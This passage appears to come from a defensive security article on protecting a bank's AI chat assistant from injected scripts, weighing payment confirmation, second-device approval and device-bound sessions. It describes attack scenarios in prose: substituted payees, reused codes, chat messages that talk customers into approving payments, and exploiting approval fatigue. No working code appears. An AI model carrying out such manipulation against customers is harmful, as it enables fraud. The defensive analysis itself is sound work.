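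The draft has fields for the payee's name and web origin but none for an account number, because it is mainly meant for confirming payments in online shops. An attacker could therefore add their own account under the name "Keller Plumbing", and the browser's window would look right. For a bank transfer, the bank should check the name against the account or include part of the account number in the name that the browser displays.

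The feature is also far from universal. Jacobs (2026) quotes a Chromium developer who said in February that one part of it, the browser-bound key, had fully launched on Windows and macOS. This extra key stays on one device even if the passkey is synchronised to others. The standard still needs two independent implementations before it can advance.

The draft's sample code uses an older method when the browser does not support the feature. An injected script could falsely report that support is missing, so the older method must make it just as hard for the script to approve a payment. The feature covers only payments, so a request to share a document or change an address needs some other form of approval.

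### Approval on a second device

The bank can get the same protection without special browser support by sending the order from its server to the customer's phone app. The app shows the payee and amount that the server will use, and the customer approves them there. The injected script has no access to the phone. At the bank that Positive Security tested, only the second-factor check stopped the researcher's script from taking money.

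What the second device displays matters more than the fact that it is separate. If the phone shows only a six-digit code, the script can prompt the customer to enter it on the page to pay the plumber, then use it for another payment. A text message showing "€240 to account ending 4471" at least lets the customer check the amount and account against the plumber's invoice.

Using a phone only as a passkey for a computer does not help either, because the computer's browser supplies the details that the phone signs. According to minutes from W3C (2026), a member of its payments group said in March that this makes it very difficult to get a trustworthy confirmation across two devices. The member suggested letting the phone's passkey software display the payment and create the record itself. A bank's own app already avoids the problem because it gets the details directly from the bank.

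A script could still try to explain away the difference by writing in the chat that Keller Plumbing uses a payment company with an unfamiliar name, and that the customer should approve the payment on their phone. The app could warn that the payee is new and that nothing in the chat can confirm who owns the account, but some customers will approve the payment anyway.

### Sessions tied to one device

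Approvals protect individual actions. Short-lived sessions limit how long an attacker can use a stolen credential, and device-bound sessions make it hard to renew that credential on another computer. *Device Bound Session Credentials*, a feature that Google developed for Chrome, combines the two. Helme, in *Device Bound Session Credentials*, explains the process:

1. After sign-in, the server asks the browser to create a bound session.
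2. The browser creates a pair of keys in the computer's security chip and sends the public key to the server. The private key stays in the chip.
3. The server issues a cookie that lasts perhaps three to five minutes.
4. Before the cookie expires, or when the user next needs it, the browser signs a challenge with the private key and receives a new cookie.

If malicious software copies the cookie to another computer, the copy works only until it expires. Ackerman, Rubery and Ehinger (2026), in *Protecting Cookies with Device Bound Session Credentials*, report that Google saw a significant reduction in session theft after introducing an early version of the feature, but they do not say how large. Chrome 146 made the feature publicly available on Windows in April 2026. Google's *Prevent account takeovers with Device Bound Session Credentials (DBSC)* (2026) says that it is on by default for Google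 Workspace users on Windows.

Device-bound session credentials do not stop requests from an injected script, because those requests come from the right browser on the right device. If the session cookie has expired, the browser gets a new one before sending the script's request. W3C's draft standard, *Device Bound Session Credentials* (2025), says that the feature will not prevent temporary access to a session while the attacker is on the user's device. The passage concerns malicious software, but an attacker's script in an open page also runs on the user's device.

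HttpOnly often already prevents an injected script from copying the session cookie. Binding the session still helps if the cookie leaks some other way, such as through a server log. Binding does not protect a login token in browser storage, like the one attackers could take from Open WebUI, unless the site replaces that token with a bound cookie.

Deploying the feature also takes care. *Everything I learned shipping Device Bound Session Credentials* describes several faults in the first version at Helme's company, Report URI. In one, the page that loaded just after sign-in could overwrite the record of the binding. When that happened, the server accepted the ordinary cookie by itself, with no error to show that the protection was gone.

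Another fault logged out genuine users. In one recorded case, renewing the cookie took 1.2 seconds, and the page sent a request with the old cookie during that time. The server treated the old cookie as stolen and ended the session. The fault rarely appeared on the developers' computers, where a renewal took a few milliseconds.

Browsers without the feature still use ordinary cookies, so a site can adopt it without locking anyone out, but people using those browsers get no extra protection. Report URI says that only Chrome has released the feature and that the computer must have secure storage for the key. W3C's *Device Bound Session Credentials explainer*, from early 2025, estimated that about 60% of Windows users had suitable hardware, a share that was growing. It put the time for one signature at 200 milliseconds typically and 600 in slow cases.

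### How often to ask the customer

Every extra confirmation takes up the customer's time. cnlab's *Secure Payment Confirmation*, a 2025 slide deck, says that the checks banks show in frames during online shopping lead many people to abandon their purchases, and that customers find these frames hard to distinguish from phishing. W3C's payment standard, which lets a customer register once and then confirm payments at many shops, aims in part to reduce such interruptions.

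Frequent approval requests can also weaken the check, because a customer who has to approve every question to the assistant may start pressing "Approve" without reading. An injected script can exploit this by waiting until the customer makes a real payment and expects a request on their phone, then submitting a false payment. The phone will show the false payment's actual payee, but the customer has to read it. Some users turn off the requests if the product lets them, as Claude's browser extension did with "Act without asking".

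The bank can reduce the number of requests by asking only about the decisions that matter most to an attacker. If it asks the customer to approve each new payee, later payments to that payee can go through without another check, up to a limit. An injected script could then repeat a payment to an approved payee, but it could not pay the attacker. The bank should ask again if the payee's account number changes.

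Reading is harder to protect this way. Customers expect to see their balance and their conversation as soon as they open the page, and an injected script can read whatever the server sends there. The bank could keep older conversations on the server until the customer asks for them and confirms on the phone. The script would then get only the current conversation, but customers would have to pick up their phones whenever they wanted to see an older one.
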